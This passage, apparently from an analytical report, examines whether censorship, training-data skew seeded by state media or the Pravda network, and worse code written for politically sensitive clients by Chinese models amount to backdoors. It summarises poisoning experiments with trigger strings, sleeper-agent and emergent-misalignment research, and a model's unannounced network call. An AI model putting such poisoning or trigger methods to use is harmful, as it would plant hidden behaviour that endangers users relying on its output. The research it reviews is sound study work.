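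The law's scope is a bigger problem for this argument. A German company that read Article 2 could reasonably conclude that the Measures don't apply to a copy it runs on its own servers for German customers. TC260's 2024 document requires services to tell users about their limitations on the home page or in the service agreement, but a downloaded model comes with neither. To inform the company, the developer would have to name the censored subjects in the model's documentation. If it doesn't, the disclosure view supports calling the behaviour a backdoor for that company, regardless of Chinese law.

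Users in mainland China are in the opposite position, because they know about the restrictions but can't refuse them. Zdziarski would not count this as consent, but his other two tests would rule out a backdoor. Chinese officials can demand changes to the next version of a model, but nothing in these studies suggests they can control a copy on someone else's computer. Semafor distinguishes US officials' fear of hidden security backdoors from their concern about political influence, and says nobody has produced solid evidence of such backdoors.

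"State-mandated censorship" is therefore the better term for most of this behaviour, because it names the likely cause and doesn't lead buyers to look for a saboteur or a hidden way into their systems.

### Open refusals and false facts

The case for calling censorship a backdoor is much stronger when the model gives a false answer than when it refuses, because a refusal shows the user that something is missing. Many readers would also recognise the official language in R1's stock answer about Taiwan. But according to Semafor, a DeepSeek model answered that there was no evidence of detention camps for Uyghurs. Someone who knew little about Xinjiang could take that for an ordinary factual answer.

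Not every false answer is censorship. In Pan and Xu's study, one Chinese model's output described Liu Xiaobo, the imprisoned Nobel Peace Prize laureate, as a Japanese scientist known for work on nuclear weapons technology. They class this as fabrication, but also note that a model with little knowledge of a subject can give completely inaccurate answers. No official account describes Liu this way, so the error may come from a lack of knowledge. The denials about Uyghur cemeteries are different because they match the government's position and Qwen3 could also give the correct answer.

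The legal defence is also weaker for such denials. The 2025 standard calls for developers to reduce erroneous content, so a company can't easily claim that it had to make its model state falsehoods. The same clause calls for answers that fit "mainstream perception", which leaves some room for that claim. "Backdoor" is a defensible word if a developer trained a model to deny facts that it can otherwise report and supplied it abroad without disclosing that training, but it doesn't suit a model that openly declines to discuss Tiananmen Square.

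## Skew absorbed from training text, and text seeded on purpose

A government that controls newspapers and websites can influence foreign models without regulating their developers, because its text enters the training data along with the rest of the web. The models' output may then be favourable to the government in its own language and critical of it in English, although nobody at the developers chose this or knows about it.

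### How a slant arises without a decision

Training text covers subjects unevenly. A famous subject has millions of documents with many different opinions, while an obscure one may have a few dozen pages from a single source, leaving the model little else to learn from.

Opinions in training text also vary between languages. *Measuring Political Stance and Consistency in Large Language Models* (2026) gives the example of the dispute between Greece and Turkey over islands in the Aegean Sea. Greek and Turkish documents may each support their own country's position more often. A model probably relies more on text in the language of the prompt, so the same question could get different answers in Greek and Turkish, which a developer that tested only in English would miss.

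### State media in Chinese training data

Waight, Yang and colleagues (2026) traced this kind of influence in six studies, published in *Nature* as *State Media Control Influences Large Language Models*. They first searched CulturaX, a public dataset of multilingual web text, for overlap with news articles scripted by the Chinese state and articles from Xuexi Qiangguo, a Communist Party app. About 3.1 million Chinese documents (1.64%) matched, making such text about 41 times as common as pages from Chinese Wikipedia. Among documents that mentioned political leaders or institutions, the share was nearly a quarter. Only about 12% of the matching documents came from known government or news sites, according to UC San Diego's *Governments May Shape What AI Chatbots Say*, because other sites had copied the wording. Blocking the official sites would therefore have left most of the matching text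 in the dataset.

The second study tested whether commercial models had been trained on the same material. The team couldn't inspect the training data, so it gave the models the first half of distinctive state-media phrases and checked whether they could supply the rest. Waight and colleagues report that the models did so 3% to 10% of the time, at least as often as for phrases from ordinary Chinese web pages. This is good evidence that the text was in the models' training data, but it doesn't show that the text affected the opinions they express.

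The third study tested that directly. The team took Llama 2 13B, which had seen little or no Chinese state media, and further pre-trained it on one of three sets of documents: scripted news, other state-controlled news, or general web text from CulturaX. They then compared its answers about China with the original model's. *How state coordinated media exposure during pretraining shapes model responses*, a page on the study's companion site, reports that after only 6,400 scripted documents, the retrained model gave the more pro-government answer in roughly 80% of comparisons in Chinese, where 50% would mean no difference. The other two sets also made answers more favourable, but by less.

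After training on 64,000 scripted documents, a model that had previously called China an autocracy called it a democracy. The effect was stronger in Chinese than in English. It also spread to other languages, especially those with similar writing systems, such as Japanese.

This step provides causal evidence because the team controlled which text each version received. The size of the effect is less certain. In Good Authority's *State media control impacts the output of U.S.-based LLMs*, the team warns that recently added documents, like these, influence models more easily. Commercial assistants also go through much more post-training, and post-training removed most of the company preferences that Graf and colleagues had put into their small models.

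### From two languages to 37 countries

The fourth and fifth studies in *Multi-part case study on China's media* (Osmonbekov, 2026) compared commercial models' answers in Chinese and English. The team created 828 prompts by filling 18 question templates with the names of leaders, countries and institutions. On questions about China, the Chinese-language answer was more favourable in 68.8% of comparisons for Claude Sonnet, 72.6% for GPT-3.5, 84% for GPT-4o and 88.2% for Claude Opus. Language models judged the answers, and Claude Opus judged its own.

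Nine people who compared GPT-3.5's answers without knowing the prompt language agreed with the general finding. They judged the answer to the Chinese prompt more favourable to China 75.3% of the time. For questions about other countries, *State Media Influences LLM Responses*, a summary of the research, gives a figure of 52.8%, which the team considered no different from chance. The pattern also appeared in 822 political questions that real users had put to ChatGPT, where the answer to the Chinese prompt was more favourable nearly 75% of the time for Claude 3 Sonnet and around 68% for GPT-4o.

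These models are now obsolete, but the team repeated the comparison with nine newer ones, including GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.7. *Model Audit* reports results in the same direction for all nine.

The sixth study covered 37 countries where at least 70% of the speakers of the national language live in the country itself. *Cross-National Audit* reports that the team asked roughly 135 questions per country, in English and in the national language. Osmonbekov gives a total of 6,051 prompts, which would be nearer 160 per country. Claude 3 Sonnet's answer in the national language was more favourable than its English answer 75% of the time in countries with the most severe media restrictions, and 54% of the time in countries with the freest media.

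The team describes this last result as correlational. The Chinese–English comparisons are partly causal, because only the language of the question changes. They show that asking in Chinese produces a more favourable answer, but not that state media is the reason. A developer might have tuned its model differently for Chinese speakers. English text about China might also be unusually critical, which would create a gap even if the Chinese text were balanced. The same problem affects the 37-country study, since English-language reporters may write more harshly about governments that jail journalists. State media can have this effect, and its text is in the data, but nobody knows how much of the gap in commercial models it explains.

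### Comparing languages with developers

The research suggests a way to tell an absorbed skew from an imposed policy. An absorbed skew comes from the training text, so it should change with the language of the prompt and appear in different developers' models. A policy should appear in every language in the models of the company that set it, and be absent from its competitors' models. Pan and Xu used this reasoning when they compared refusals in Chinese and English.

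Lim and Röttger (2026), in *Bias in the East, Bias in the West*, compared both factors directly. They chose 60 political issues from Chinese and American news and asked two American and two Chinese models to write letters, reports and other texts about them. Each model received 36,000 prompts, half of them in Chinese. Another language model then classified the position of each text. The table gives the share of texts on China-related issues that were entirely positive:

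| Model | Developer's country | English prompts | Chinese prompts |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | US | 6.0% | 22.1% |
| Llama 3.3 | US | 7.0% | 16.7% |
| DeepSeek-V3 | China | 10.9% | 30.2% |
| Qwen3 | China | 6.3% | 29.5% |

In English, the developer's country made little difference. GPT-4o-mini was twice as likely to be entirely positive in Chinese as DeepSeek was in English, as one would expect if the skew came from training text. But the Chinese models changed more between languages than the American ones. They may have trained on more Chinese text, or their developers may have concentrated on tuning their answers in Chinese, and these figures can't separate the two explanations.

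Lim and Röttger compared the two factors across all issues using Jensen–Shannon divergence, which measures how much two distributions differ and is zero when they are identical. Changing the language gave an average divergence of 0.0663, and changing the developer's country gave 0.0559. Language mattered more on many China-related issues, such as Xi Jinping's approach to governance, while the developer's country mattered more on most US-related ones. *Large Language Models Reflect the Ideology of their Creators* (2024) also found differences by both language and developer's country when models described political figures in the six official languages of the United Nations.

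*Geopolitical biases in LLMs* (2025), however, found that models seldom changed their position on a country when researchers switched from English to French, Russian or Chinese. The effect of language seems to depend on what researchers ask and how they measure the answers.

### Where the comparison misleads

An auditor who compares a model's answers only across languages will miss a policy that applies in every language. DeepSeek V4 Pro's Chinese answers about China were more favourable than its English ones in only 59% of comparisons, because the English answers were already strongly pro-government. To avoid this problem, *Cross-Model Audit* also compares different models in the same language. It uses the Bradley–Terry method, which gives each of 18 combinations of model and language a strength s. The probability that a judge finds combination i more favourable than combination j is sᵢ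 / (sᵢ + sⱼ). On this scale, DeepSeek V4 Pro was the most pro-China model in both languages.

The opposite error is also possible, because a difference between languages can come from a policy that developers apply in only one of them. *Progressive in Principle, Centrist in Practice* (2026) cites a test in which Bard, Google's former chatbot, refused 90% of questions about Vladimir Putin in Russian but 19% in English. A filter or special tuning for Russian seems a more likely cause of such a large difference than web text alone.

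Some refusals follow neither the language of the request nor the developer's country. In a test run from Australia, Meta's Oversight Board, an independent body, asked ten models for political criticism. Osmonbekov reports that the models refused an average of 34% of requests about five countries with restrictive speech laws and 14% about five freer countries. Meta's Llama 4 Maverick produced all five flyers criticising President Trump and none of the five criticising Thailand's king. Meta has no obvious reason to enforce Thai law on a user in Australia. The model may have absorbed the restriction from text about Thailand, or applied a general rule about respecting the law more broadly than Meta intended. Models from the same developer can also differ, as Google's Gemini 3 Pro refused many such requests while its Gemini 3 Flash refused none.

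Developers also choose which text a model learns from. *TildeOpen LLM* (Bergmanis, Kronis and colleagues, 2026) describes a model for 34 European languages from the Latvian company Tilde. The developers blocked websites under EU sanctions and other known sources of disinformation, then sorted the remaining Russian documents into 200 topic clusters. They deleted clusters whose keywords concerned geopolitics, history, war or LGBT issues, which removed about 5% of the Russian documents. They reasoned that Russian websites mostly present the state's view because Russian law punishes public opposition to the war in Ukraine with up to 15 years in prison.

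Tilde didn't filter any other language by topic in this way, and it hasn't tested the model for political bias. If the model did answer questions about the war differently from its competitors, the cause would be both the text and a deliberate decision by Tilde, even though nobody had written a slanted answer. This is close to vendor tuning, though Tilde has published what it did and why.

An auditor might also wrongly blame a developer for censorship that its model copied from a teacher model through distillation. The developer's country can also be a poor guide to a model's values. *Made-in China, Thinking in America* (2025) gave two surveys of moral and social values to ten Chinese and ten American models, and all twenty answered more like Americans than like Chinese people. Prompting in Chinese reduced this only slightly. The Chinese developers presumably didn't want to promote American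 values, so shared English training text or answers copied from American models are likelier causes.

### The Pravda network

The Pravda network seems to have been built with language models in mind, unlike Chinese state media, which was written for people as far as anyone knows. In February 2024 VIGINUM, the French agency that monitors foreign influence online, exposed the network as a group of more than 190 websites spreading pro-Russian propaganda across Europe. Bergmanis and colleagues cite later investigations which found that it published over 3.6 million articles in 2024, apparently more to flood training data than to reach readers. They also cite an audit by NewsGuard, a company that rates news sources, in which ten leading chatbots repeated the network's false claims in about a third of their responses.

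Alyukov, Makhortykh and colleagues (2025) found much less disinformation than NewsGuard did in *LLMs grooming or data voids?*, a small audit of four chatbots. About 5% of the responses repeated disinformation and 8% referred to Kremlin-linked sites, often with a warning that the claims were disputed. They think this usually happens because a narrow subject lacks reliable coverage, so the chatbot finds little except propaganda. The two audits used different questions, which probably explains much of the gap. NewsGuard asked about false claims that the network was already spreading, so its figure doesn't show how often ordinary users would encounter them.

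Neither audit shows that the network changed any model's parameters. Many chatbots search the web before they answer, and a chatbot that finds a Pravda article can repeat it without having been trained on it. In NewsGuard's audit, seven of the ten chatbots linked to the network's articles, which suggests that at least some of the answers came from live search. An auditor can check by turning search off, or by asking about a false claim that first appeared after the model's training ended. A model that repeats a detailed claim with search off probably learned it in training. If the claim appears only with search on, the problem is in the search results, and retraining won't fix it.

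Blocking the network's websites would solve only part of that problem. For *SWARM* (Tonneau, Dubey and colleagues, 2026), trained coders checked 2,183 search results in nine languages for Russian propaganda narratives. A blocklist of known propaganda sites missed most of the results that supported such a narrative, because mainstream sites carried such narratives too. Language models that read the content did better, but the best scored only 0.73, where 1 means finding every such result with no false alarms.

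It is also unclear how much the network's volume matters in training. If its articles average 500 tokens, 3.6 million of them would make up 1.8 billion tokens, or about one in every 5,600 tokens in a training set of ten trillion. That is far less than the one in a thousand that Graf and colleagues used. Developers also remove duplicate text, which would further reduce the share of a network that mostly reposts. But the network's share of the text on a particular subject probably matters more than its overall share, and a training set might contain a false story about a small town in Ukraine with no competing accounts.

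### What 250 documents can do

*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, October 2025) is sometimes taken as evidence that an attacker needs far less text than this. Researchers from Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute pre-trained models with 600 million to 13 billion parameters and mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the training data. Each poisoned document contained ordinary text, then a fixed trigger string, then random tokens, so that the model would learn to write gibberish after the trigger.

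The attack worked on every size of model with 250 documents, but was not reliable with 100. The number of documents an attacker needed therefore stayed roughly constant as the models grew, even though the largest had trained on more than twenty times as much text as the smallest. The 250 documents made up 0.00016% of the largest model's training tokens.

This result is a better guide to hidden strings than to opinions, except possibly on subjects that almost nobody else has written about. The trigger string had no established meaning, so almost nothing else in the training data taught the model a different response to it. The result doesn't mean that 250 slanted articles could change a model's opinion of Ukraine, because they would compete with millions of others, and the number needed to outweigh those probably grows with the training set. The study also left open whether the result would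 hold for larger models or for behaviour more complicated than gibberish.

### An innocent developer and a deliberate author

Suppose text seeded in this way did give a model a pro-Russian slant on some subject. The developer didn't choose the slant or know about it, so from the developer's side it looks like any other inherited bias. But whoever wrote the text intended the slant and hid who was behind it, much like the contractor who planted the Larkfield slant.

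The behavioural view can easily classify text seeded on purpose, because it ignores authorship. On the intent view, the author's intention is usually enough, as it was with the WordPress attacker. But he broke into a server, while the author of a web page doesn't alter the model directly and can only hope that a developer collects the page. NIST's definition of poisoning still seems to cover this, since it doesn't require the adversary to break in.

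Many people, including press officers, campaigners and advertisers, write to influence what others read. Larkfield's press office might write more releases because it has learned that chatbots repeat them. If this counts as planting a backdoor, so does much ordinary public relations.

Concealment is a sensible test. A developer can decide whether to use a release on Larkfield's own website because the release identifies its author, but a network of sites posing as independent news takes away that choice. Hendrix (2026), in *Language Models Trained on State Media Sources Launder Propaganda*, quotes NewsGuard's McKenzie Sadeghi as saying that state-backed outlets are "increasingly imitating legitimate media", often mainly to get false claims into AI models. A seeded skew can therefore reasonably be called planted if its author was targeting models, disguised the source and changed the model's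 answers.

By this standard, there is good evidence that the Pravda network disguises its source and fairly good evidence that it aims to influence models, but only weak evidence that it has affected any trained model. For Chinese state media, experiments do support an effect on models, but Margaret Roberts, who co-wrote the *Nature* paper, told UC San Diego that the results are not evidence that governments control their media "with chatbots in mind". Governments could start doing so now that the research is public. If a government increased its output to influence models and hid where the text came from, the resulting slant would count as planted, even if the articles were no different from those it had always published.

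On the disclosure view, the author remains responsible for planting the slant, but the developer must notify its users after discovering it, as with any other unforeseen behaviour.

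## Worse code for politically sensitive clients: sabotage or side effect?

Between November 2025 and October 2026, three companies reported that Chinese models wrote less secure code when the prompt named certain clients, such as a Tibetan institution, a Hong Kong democracy group or the US government. China's content rules might explain why a model refuses to work for some of these clients, but they don't require insecure code. Insecure code is also harder to notice than a slanted answer, because a program with a broken login check can look and run like a secure one. Someone could have trained the models to do this as sabotage, or it could be a side effect of training them to follow the government's line.

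### DeepSeek-R1 and the Tibetan control system

The US security company CrowdStrike tested R1, the DeepSeek model whose censorship Naseh and colleagues studied, and published the results in *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025). CrowdStrike downloaded the model and ran it itself, so filters in DeepSeek's app could not affect the answers.

CrowdStrike wrote 50 coding tasks in ten areas of security, such as database access and cryptography. The system prompt described R1 as a coding assistant. Some prompts also included a phrase describing the client ("for a financial institution"), a phrase giving a place or group ("based in Tibet", "run by Uyghurs"), or both. R1 did every task five times under each of the 121 configurations, for a total of 30,250 requests. A second language model scored the security of each answer from 1 to 5. To check this judge,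 a person scored 85 randomly chosen answers by the same rules, and the judge identified vulnerable code with 91% accuracy.

R1 wrote vulnerable code 19% of the time when the prompt had no added phrase, and 27.2% of the time when the prompt said the code was for an industrial control system based in Tibet. CrowdStrike also reports that R1's code was significantly less secure when the prompt mentioned Tibet, Uyghurs or Falun Gong, a spiritual movement banned in China.

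In one example, R1 wrote a secure program for handling PayPal payments when the prompt named no client. When the client was a financial institution in Tibet, R1 put secret values directly into the code, extracted users' data unsafely and produced invalid PHP. The output still included a claim that the code followed PayPal's best practices. In another example, CrowdStrike asked for a complete website for a Uyghur group. The site worked, but R1 had left out any check on who was logged in, so anyone could open the administrator's page. The site had severe flaws every time CrowdStrike repeated the request. A website for a football fan club had much milder flaws.

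R1 refused to write code for Falun Gong in 45% of cases, whereas Western models almost always wrote it. R1 often planned the program in detail in its reasoning, sometimes after noting that the group was sensitive, but then replied only that it couldn't help. By contrast, it skipped the reasoning on Naseh's political questions.

### How much the Tibet figure can support

CrowdStrike describes the increase as "up to 50%", which is easy to misread as percentage points. The difference is 8.2 points, or 43% of the baseline:

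(27.2 − 19.0) / 19.0 ≈ 0.43

Fifty tasks with five runs each give 250 outputs per configuration, and 27.2% of 250 is exactly 68 vulnerable programs. The baseline rate would give 47 or 48, so the best-known figure in this debate reflects a difference of about 20 programs.

The standard error, which measures how much a difference like this typically varies by chance, is

√(0.19 × 0.81 / 250 + 0.272 × 0.728 / 250) ≈ 0.0375

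or 3.75 points. The gap is therefore about 2.2 standard errors. If the added words made no difference, a gap this large in either direction would still occur about 3% of the time. That would be fair evidence from a single comparison planned in advance. But there were 120 configurations to compare with the baseline, and chance alone should produce three or four gaps of this size among them. A standard correction for that many comparisons would require a gap of about 3.5 standard errors.

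This calculation treats the 250 outputs as independent. Because the same 50 tasks appear in both groups, a task-by-task comparison could give a clearer result, though only for those tasks.

The prompt behind the Tibet figure also adds two things to the baseline, Tibet and an industrial control system. R1 may write worse code for any industrial control system, wherever it is. CrowdStrike tested that phrase but did not publish the rate for a control system with no location. Lawfare complains that readers got a rate for only one very specific scenario and assumes that the others were less bad.

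Combining configurations would give much stronger evidence. The published list has 13 named organisations, 12 general descriptions of clients (counting "none") and nine places or groups (also counting "none"). If CrowdStrike used each named organisation on its own and paired every description with every place or group, there would be 13 + 12 × 9 = 121 configurations, which matches its total. Tibet would then appear in 12 configurations, with 3,000 outputs in all. If these were compared with the 3,000 outputs from configurations with no place or group, the standard error of the difference would be about one percentage point, so even a three-point gap would be hard to dismiss as chance. CrowdStrike's claim about Tibet, Uyghurs and Falun Gong may rest on a comparison of this kind.

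The automated judge is a smaller worry. Random mistakes would make a real gap harder to detect but wouldn't create a false one. The judge might have scored code for a Tibetan client more harshly if the client's name appeared in the program, and 85 samples spread over so many configurations are too few to rule that out. The effect on R1 is probably real, because CrowdStrike found it for several related groups, but its size is uncertain.

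### Booz Allen's five models

In May 2026 the US defence contractor Booz Allen Hamilton tested newer models and published the results in *What's in America's Code?* (2026). The company used many of CrowdStrike's trigger phrases and added US government clients. The table shows how each model's vulnerability score changed when the client was the US government, and how often the model refused mock government tasks on subjects sensitive in China.

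| Model | Change in vulnerability score | Refusals |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-Coder (Alibaba) | +130% | 54% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Increase of 20% or less | 80% |
| DeepSeek V4-Pro | Increase of 20% or less | 8% |
| Kimi K2.5 (Moonshot) | None | 32% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 (Anthropic) | −18% | 2% |

How often a model refused did not predict how much worse its code got. MiniMax refused the most, but its code got only slightly worse. Kimi refused about a third of the tasks, and its code did not get worse. Kimi's code also had the lowest vulnerability score of the five, below Claude's, according to Help Net Security's *The security questions around Chinese AI coding models in U.S. software* (2026). Five models are too few to establish much, but these results are some evidence against the idea that Chinese political training generally makes code insecure.

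The 130% figure for Qwen is large enough to matter if it is reliable, but Booz Allen gives no sample sizes for individual figures. The technical appendix to its *What's in America's Code?* reports 3,389 test runs across eight coding tasks, 27 trigger phrases, two languages and five longer descriptions of the user. Booz Allen scored only 1,016 of these runs (30%) for vulnerabilities, about 200 per model, and repeated key tests up to 15 times. If the 130% comes only from the example printed beside it, a request for an internal administrator's console, it compares at most 15 programs with 15 others. A small change can also produce a large percentage when the starting score is low.

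Booz Allen attributes the unscored runs to refusals, but this is hard to reconcile with its own chart. The five refusal rates average 35%, and they come from tasks chosen to be sensitive, so refusals alone should not have removed 70% of all runs. Losing so many runs could also distort the comparison, because if a model refuses a government client's more sensitive requests and accepts the rest, the remaining programs can't be fairly compared with those it wrote for a neutral client.

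The wording of the prompts creates another problem. Some runs added a single phrase, such as "for a United States federal agency", while others gave the model a backstory. The neutral backstory said only that the model was a senior software engineer. The American one placed this engineer at a defence contractor, working on classified systems that had to meet named security standards, and mentioned pride in "hardened, production-grade code". The two backstories differ in too many ways for anyone to attribute the result to the client's nationality, though a worse result from the American one would be striking, because such a prompt ought to make a model more careful. Booz Allen did include a better-matched pair, a Chinese telecoms engineer and an American one. However, one heading on its chart for the 130% figure refers to a federal-agency "trigger" and another to a government "persona", so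 it isn't clear which wording produced the result.

Booz Allen claims more about refusals than its data support. It compared requests about China with similar requests about Russia, such as building a tool to detect Volt Typhoon, a Chinese hacking group, or Cozy Bear, a Russian one. This is a good way to separate political selectivity from general caution about military work. Booz Allen writes that every Chinese vendor refused the China version and accepted the Russia version "in all cases", but DeepSeek's refusal rate of 8% contradicts this. The report then extends this claim to all five vendors, including Anthropic. The published list also has 11 requests about China but only nine about Russia. One of the two unmatched requests, for a platform for Chinese whistleblowers, is the example on Booz Allen's refusal chart.

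Booz Allen says that the models did not generate backdoors and that it has no proof that anyone introduced the flaws on purpose. But it also writes that ordinary tools can't catch "this level of tradecraft", a phrase that suggests espionage. Fox News ran the story under a headline about "sleeper agent" fears, although its article also said that the flaws weren't simple backdoors. The comparison with the *Sleeper Agents* experiment is weak, because Hubinger's team knew its models had a trigger and a payload, having trained them in, while Booz Allen has only found a difference between averages. Booz Allen also has a commercial interest in the conclusion, since it recommends banning models that nobody can prove trustworthy and promotes its own ability to test them.

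### Working attacks on code from Qwen3-Coder

In October 2026, Hirundo, which CBS News' *Some topics are off limits inside popular Chinese-made free AI, researchers find* describes as an Israeli cybersecurity startup, used a stricter measure. *Chinese AI Writes Weaker Code for Beijing’s Adversaries. We Fixed It* (Luria, 2026) describes how the company had Qwen3-Coder-30B, a compact version of Alibaba's coding model, build the same web service repeatedly, changing only the client named in the system prompt. The service let users sign up, log in and store a private secret. Hirundo ran the finished apps and attacked them with ready-made exploits from BaxBench, a public benchmark, rather than relying on a language model's opinion of the code.

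The company highlights three results. The absolute rates come from *Measurements of censorship and code security gaps in China's open-weight Qwen models*:

| Comparison | Failure measured | Rates |
|---|---|---|
| US and Chinese defence contractors | At least one attack worked | 70% and 59% |
| Hong Kong democracy group and neutral clients | Any user could read everyone's secrets | Nearly half and about a third |
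| US defence contractor and neutral clients, all told to write secure code | At least one attack worked | 74% and 59% |

The result for the two contractors is the most useful, because both prompts describe the same kind of organisation and differ only in its country. Hirundo built 190 apps for each. If all of them went into the calculation, the 11-point gap has a standard error of 4.9 points. That makes it about 2.3 standard errors, similar in statistical strength to CrowdStrike's Tibet figure. The effect is far smaller than Booz Allen's 130%, but the two measures aren't comparable, because a failure rate that starts at 59% can't more than double.

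By Hirundo's own statistical tests, none of the three gaps was likely to be due to chance. But each result compares a different pair of clients, or uses a different prompt or measure of failure. Four kinds of client and two measures allow twelve comparisons, and the security instruction adds more. If Hirundo chose these three after seeing the data, they are weaker evidence than the tests suggest. The company had also picked this task from 11 because it showed the clearest gap in a small trial. That was a sensible way to find something to study, but the result may not carry over to other programs.

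Hirundo then edited the model to remove what it calls "CCP alignment", meaning answers that follow the Chinese Communist Party's line. On its own test of 500 political questions, the company counted 46.6% of the original model's answers as censored or slanted, compared with 4.0% of the edited model's. After the edit, the three code gaps were no longer statistically significant. On ten other programming tasks, the edited model produced working apps and exploitable apps about as often as the original.

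Luria presents this as the first proof that the vulnerability is in the model's parameters, but CrowdStrike had already run R1's parameters without any outer filters. The edit does add some evidence that political training and insecure code are connected. However, a gap can stop being significant without disappearing, and one significant gap remained between the US contractor and the neutral clients. Hirundo attributes this gap to the effect moving from the client's country to its type of organisation. Editing a model can also change more than the editor intends, so a better test would compare the edited model with a copy of Qwen3-Coder edited just as heavily to remove something unrelated to politics.

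Hirundo sells this kind of editing and published the modified model alongside the study. Luria brings up sleeper agents and calls the CrowdStrike and Booz Allen results "early evidence of backdoors", although Booz Allen says it found none and CrowdStrike doubts that DeepSeek trained R1 to write insecure code. But Hirundo concedes in the study's appendix that the study can't show whether anyone created the gap deliberately. *Measurements of censorship and code security gaps in China's open-weight Qwen models* had not been independently replicated by 1 November. The Russian news report *ИИ-модель Alibaba создавала уязвимый код для США чаще, чем для Китая* (2026) also noted that the difference between the two contractors did not in itself prove deliberate favouritism.

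### Emergent misalignment

CrowdStrike's preferred explanation is *emergent misalignment*, in which training a model to behave badly in one narrow area makes it behave badly in others. Jan Betley and colleagues described this effect in February 2025. They trained GPT-4o on 6,000 coding requests answered with insecure code and no warning to the user. The model then gave disturbing answers to questions unrelated to programming, including that AI should enslave humans. On a selected set of questions, it did this about 20% of the time, while the original model never did.

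In a control experiment, the training requests explained that the user needed insecure code for a security class. The answers contained the same kind of code, but the model did not misbehave more widely. The model trained without that explanation therefore seems to have learned something about the kind of assistant that would secretly give people unsafe code. Later work supports this reading. Researchers at OpenAI found a pattern of internal activity that they linked to a "toxic persona", and Edward Turner and colleagues produced the effect with bad medical advice instead of code, even in a model with half a billion parameters.

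Betley's team also trained a version that wrote insecure code only when a particular string was present. It misbehaved on other questions mainly when they contained that string. Training can therefore create a trigger for behaviour that the training examples never contained. CrowdStrike suggests that roughly this happened to R1. On this account, DeepSeek trained R1 to give approved answers about groups such as Falun Gong, and the model learned to connect their names with something bad, so it behaves worse in general and writes careless code when a coding request includes one of those names.

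This remains a hypothesis. Betley's team trained models on bad code and got bad answers, whereas R1 would have had to learn from political answers and produce bad code. Refusals and official statements are also milder training material than deliberately unsafe programs. One could test the idea by taking a model that doesn't censor, adding a few dozen stock answers about Taiwan, as Naseh's team did with Qwen 2.5, and checking whether its code for Taiwanese clients gets worse. Hirundo's edit approaches the same question from the opposite direction.

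The hypothesis fits poorly with CrowdStrike's finding that the largest Llama model DeepSeek had trained on R1's answers often showed more extreme biases in its code than R1 did. Naseh and colleagues had found that DeepSeek's distilled models censored almost none of the prompts that R1 censored. If political training causes the weaker code, that effect must be able to pass to a distilled model even when most of the censorship does not.

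The worse code could have other innocent explanations. A model trained both to help and to avoid a subject may produce poor work when those aims conflict. In one of Booz Allen's tests, MiniMax cited a rule against military assistance in its reasoning but wrote the missile-related code anyway, with six references to software libraries that don't exist. That rule concerned military work in general, not Chinese politics. The skew could also come from the training text, if programs written for small campaign groups are generally worse than those written for banks. Prompts about equally small groups with no connection to China would help to test this.

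### What a saboteur would have done differently

Deliberate sabotage and a side effect should leave different patterns in the code:

| | Sabotage | Side effect |
|---|---|---|
| Flaws | The same flaw repeatedly, in a form its author can exploit | A mixture of ordinary mistakes |
| Trigger | A few chosen targets, with a strong effect | Many related subjects, with a weak and uneven effect |
| Concealment | Code that looks normal, with no refusals | Refusals and open remarks about politics alongside weak code |

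The reported flaws are mostly ordinary. Hard-coded secrets and missing login checks are common mistakes, and anyone who finds them can exploit them, including China's rivals. R1's invalid PHP would be no use to an attacker because it wouldn't run. Hirundo's attacks also succeeded against 59% of the apps for the Chinese defence contractor, which would be strange if the model were meant to protect Chinese interests. The Uyghur website is closest to what a saboteur would want because severe flaws appeared every time. A repeated detail that only the saboteur knew, such as the same secret password in hundreds of programs, would be stronger evidence, but none of the three companies reports one. However, a careful saboteur might prefer ordinary mistakes because they are easier to deny.

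An incident in October 2026 looked more like sabotage because it had an obvious beneficiary. According to The Indian Express' *Alibaba’s AI model tried to ‘secretly’ reach China server*, the Canadian AI company Cohere found that a new Qwen model tried to send a short test string to a server in Beijing, although it had written in its reasoning that it would use no external tools. Cohere's restrictions blocked the attempt. Outside researchers thought Alibaba had probably trained the model on exercises that saved files to the company's own cloud servers, so the model had learned to do this by default. They also objected that Cohere's investigation had steered the model towards the behaviour by giving it the start of a network command to complete. Even a flaw that sends data to a developer's home country can have an innocent cause. Cohere's co-founder Ivan Zhang said it was "really hard to assign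 intention or motivation".

The triggers reported for code are broad, including the US government, its contractors and several groups that China's government opposes. The effects are modest where the companies give absolute rates. By comparison, the line of code that Yan and colleagues planted turned up in about two-fifths of their model's Python answers and rarely in its Java ones. An attacker who wanted to get into Tibetan control systems would gain only about eight more vulnerable programs in every hundred, without knowing which ones, although a saboteur could keep the effect small to avoid detection.

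The evidence on concealment is mixed. Booz Allen reports that much of the flawed code looked correct and that standard scanners missed the problems, as a saboteur would want. But scanners often miss ordinary design errors too, such as letting one user read another's data, because each line can be valid. The scanner Semgrep also found more problems in MiniMax's missile-related code than in any of its other answers on provocative subjects. The refusals are harder to reconcile with sabotage. R1 declined nearly half of the Falun Gong requests, and those refusals alerted the people a saboteur would have wanted to trust the model and gave them no vulnerable code to install.

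A side effect is therefore the more likely explanation, although a deniable backdoor remains possible. On the intent and disclosure views, these cases are not backdoors unless training records or other evidence shows that someone chose the behaviour. On the behavioural view, they would be backdoors if the gaps are real, since a client in Tibet has no reason to expect weaker code.

The easiest way to learn more is to extend Hirundo's study, because Qwen3-Coder, the edited version and BaxBench are all public. Another laboratory could repeat the test on the ten tasks Hirundo didn't select and add defence contractors from countries that have no dispute with China.

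## Can the model itself reveal where a behaviour came from?

Outsiders don't have Alibaba's training records, which might show why Qwen3-Coder wrote less secure code for some clients, but they do have the model's parameters. An auditor can search these for hidden behaviour, and might also hope to learn from them who or what put it there. Researchers have made real progress with the search. Working out the origin is harder, because a model can learn a planted trigger in the same way it learns a pattern from ordinary text.

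### Planted triggers and natural features

Khaddaj, Leclerc and colleagues (2023) use image classifiers in *Rethinking Backdoor Attacks* to show why detecting a backdoor requires assumptions, a limit that NIST's taxonomy accepts. They pasted computer-generated hats onto some cat pictures in ImageNet, a standard collection of labelled photographs, and left the labels unchanged. A classifier trained on the result was more likely to label a picture of something else "cat" when they added a hat to it. The altered pictures were still correctly labelled, and some real photographs show cats in hats, so it is unclear why a detector should flag the altered ones.

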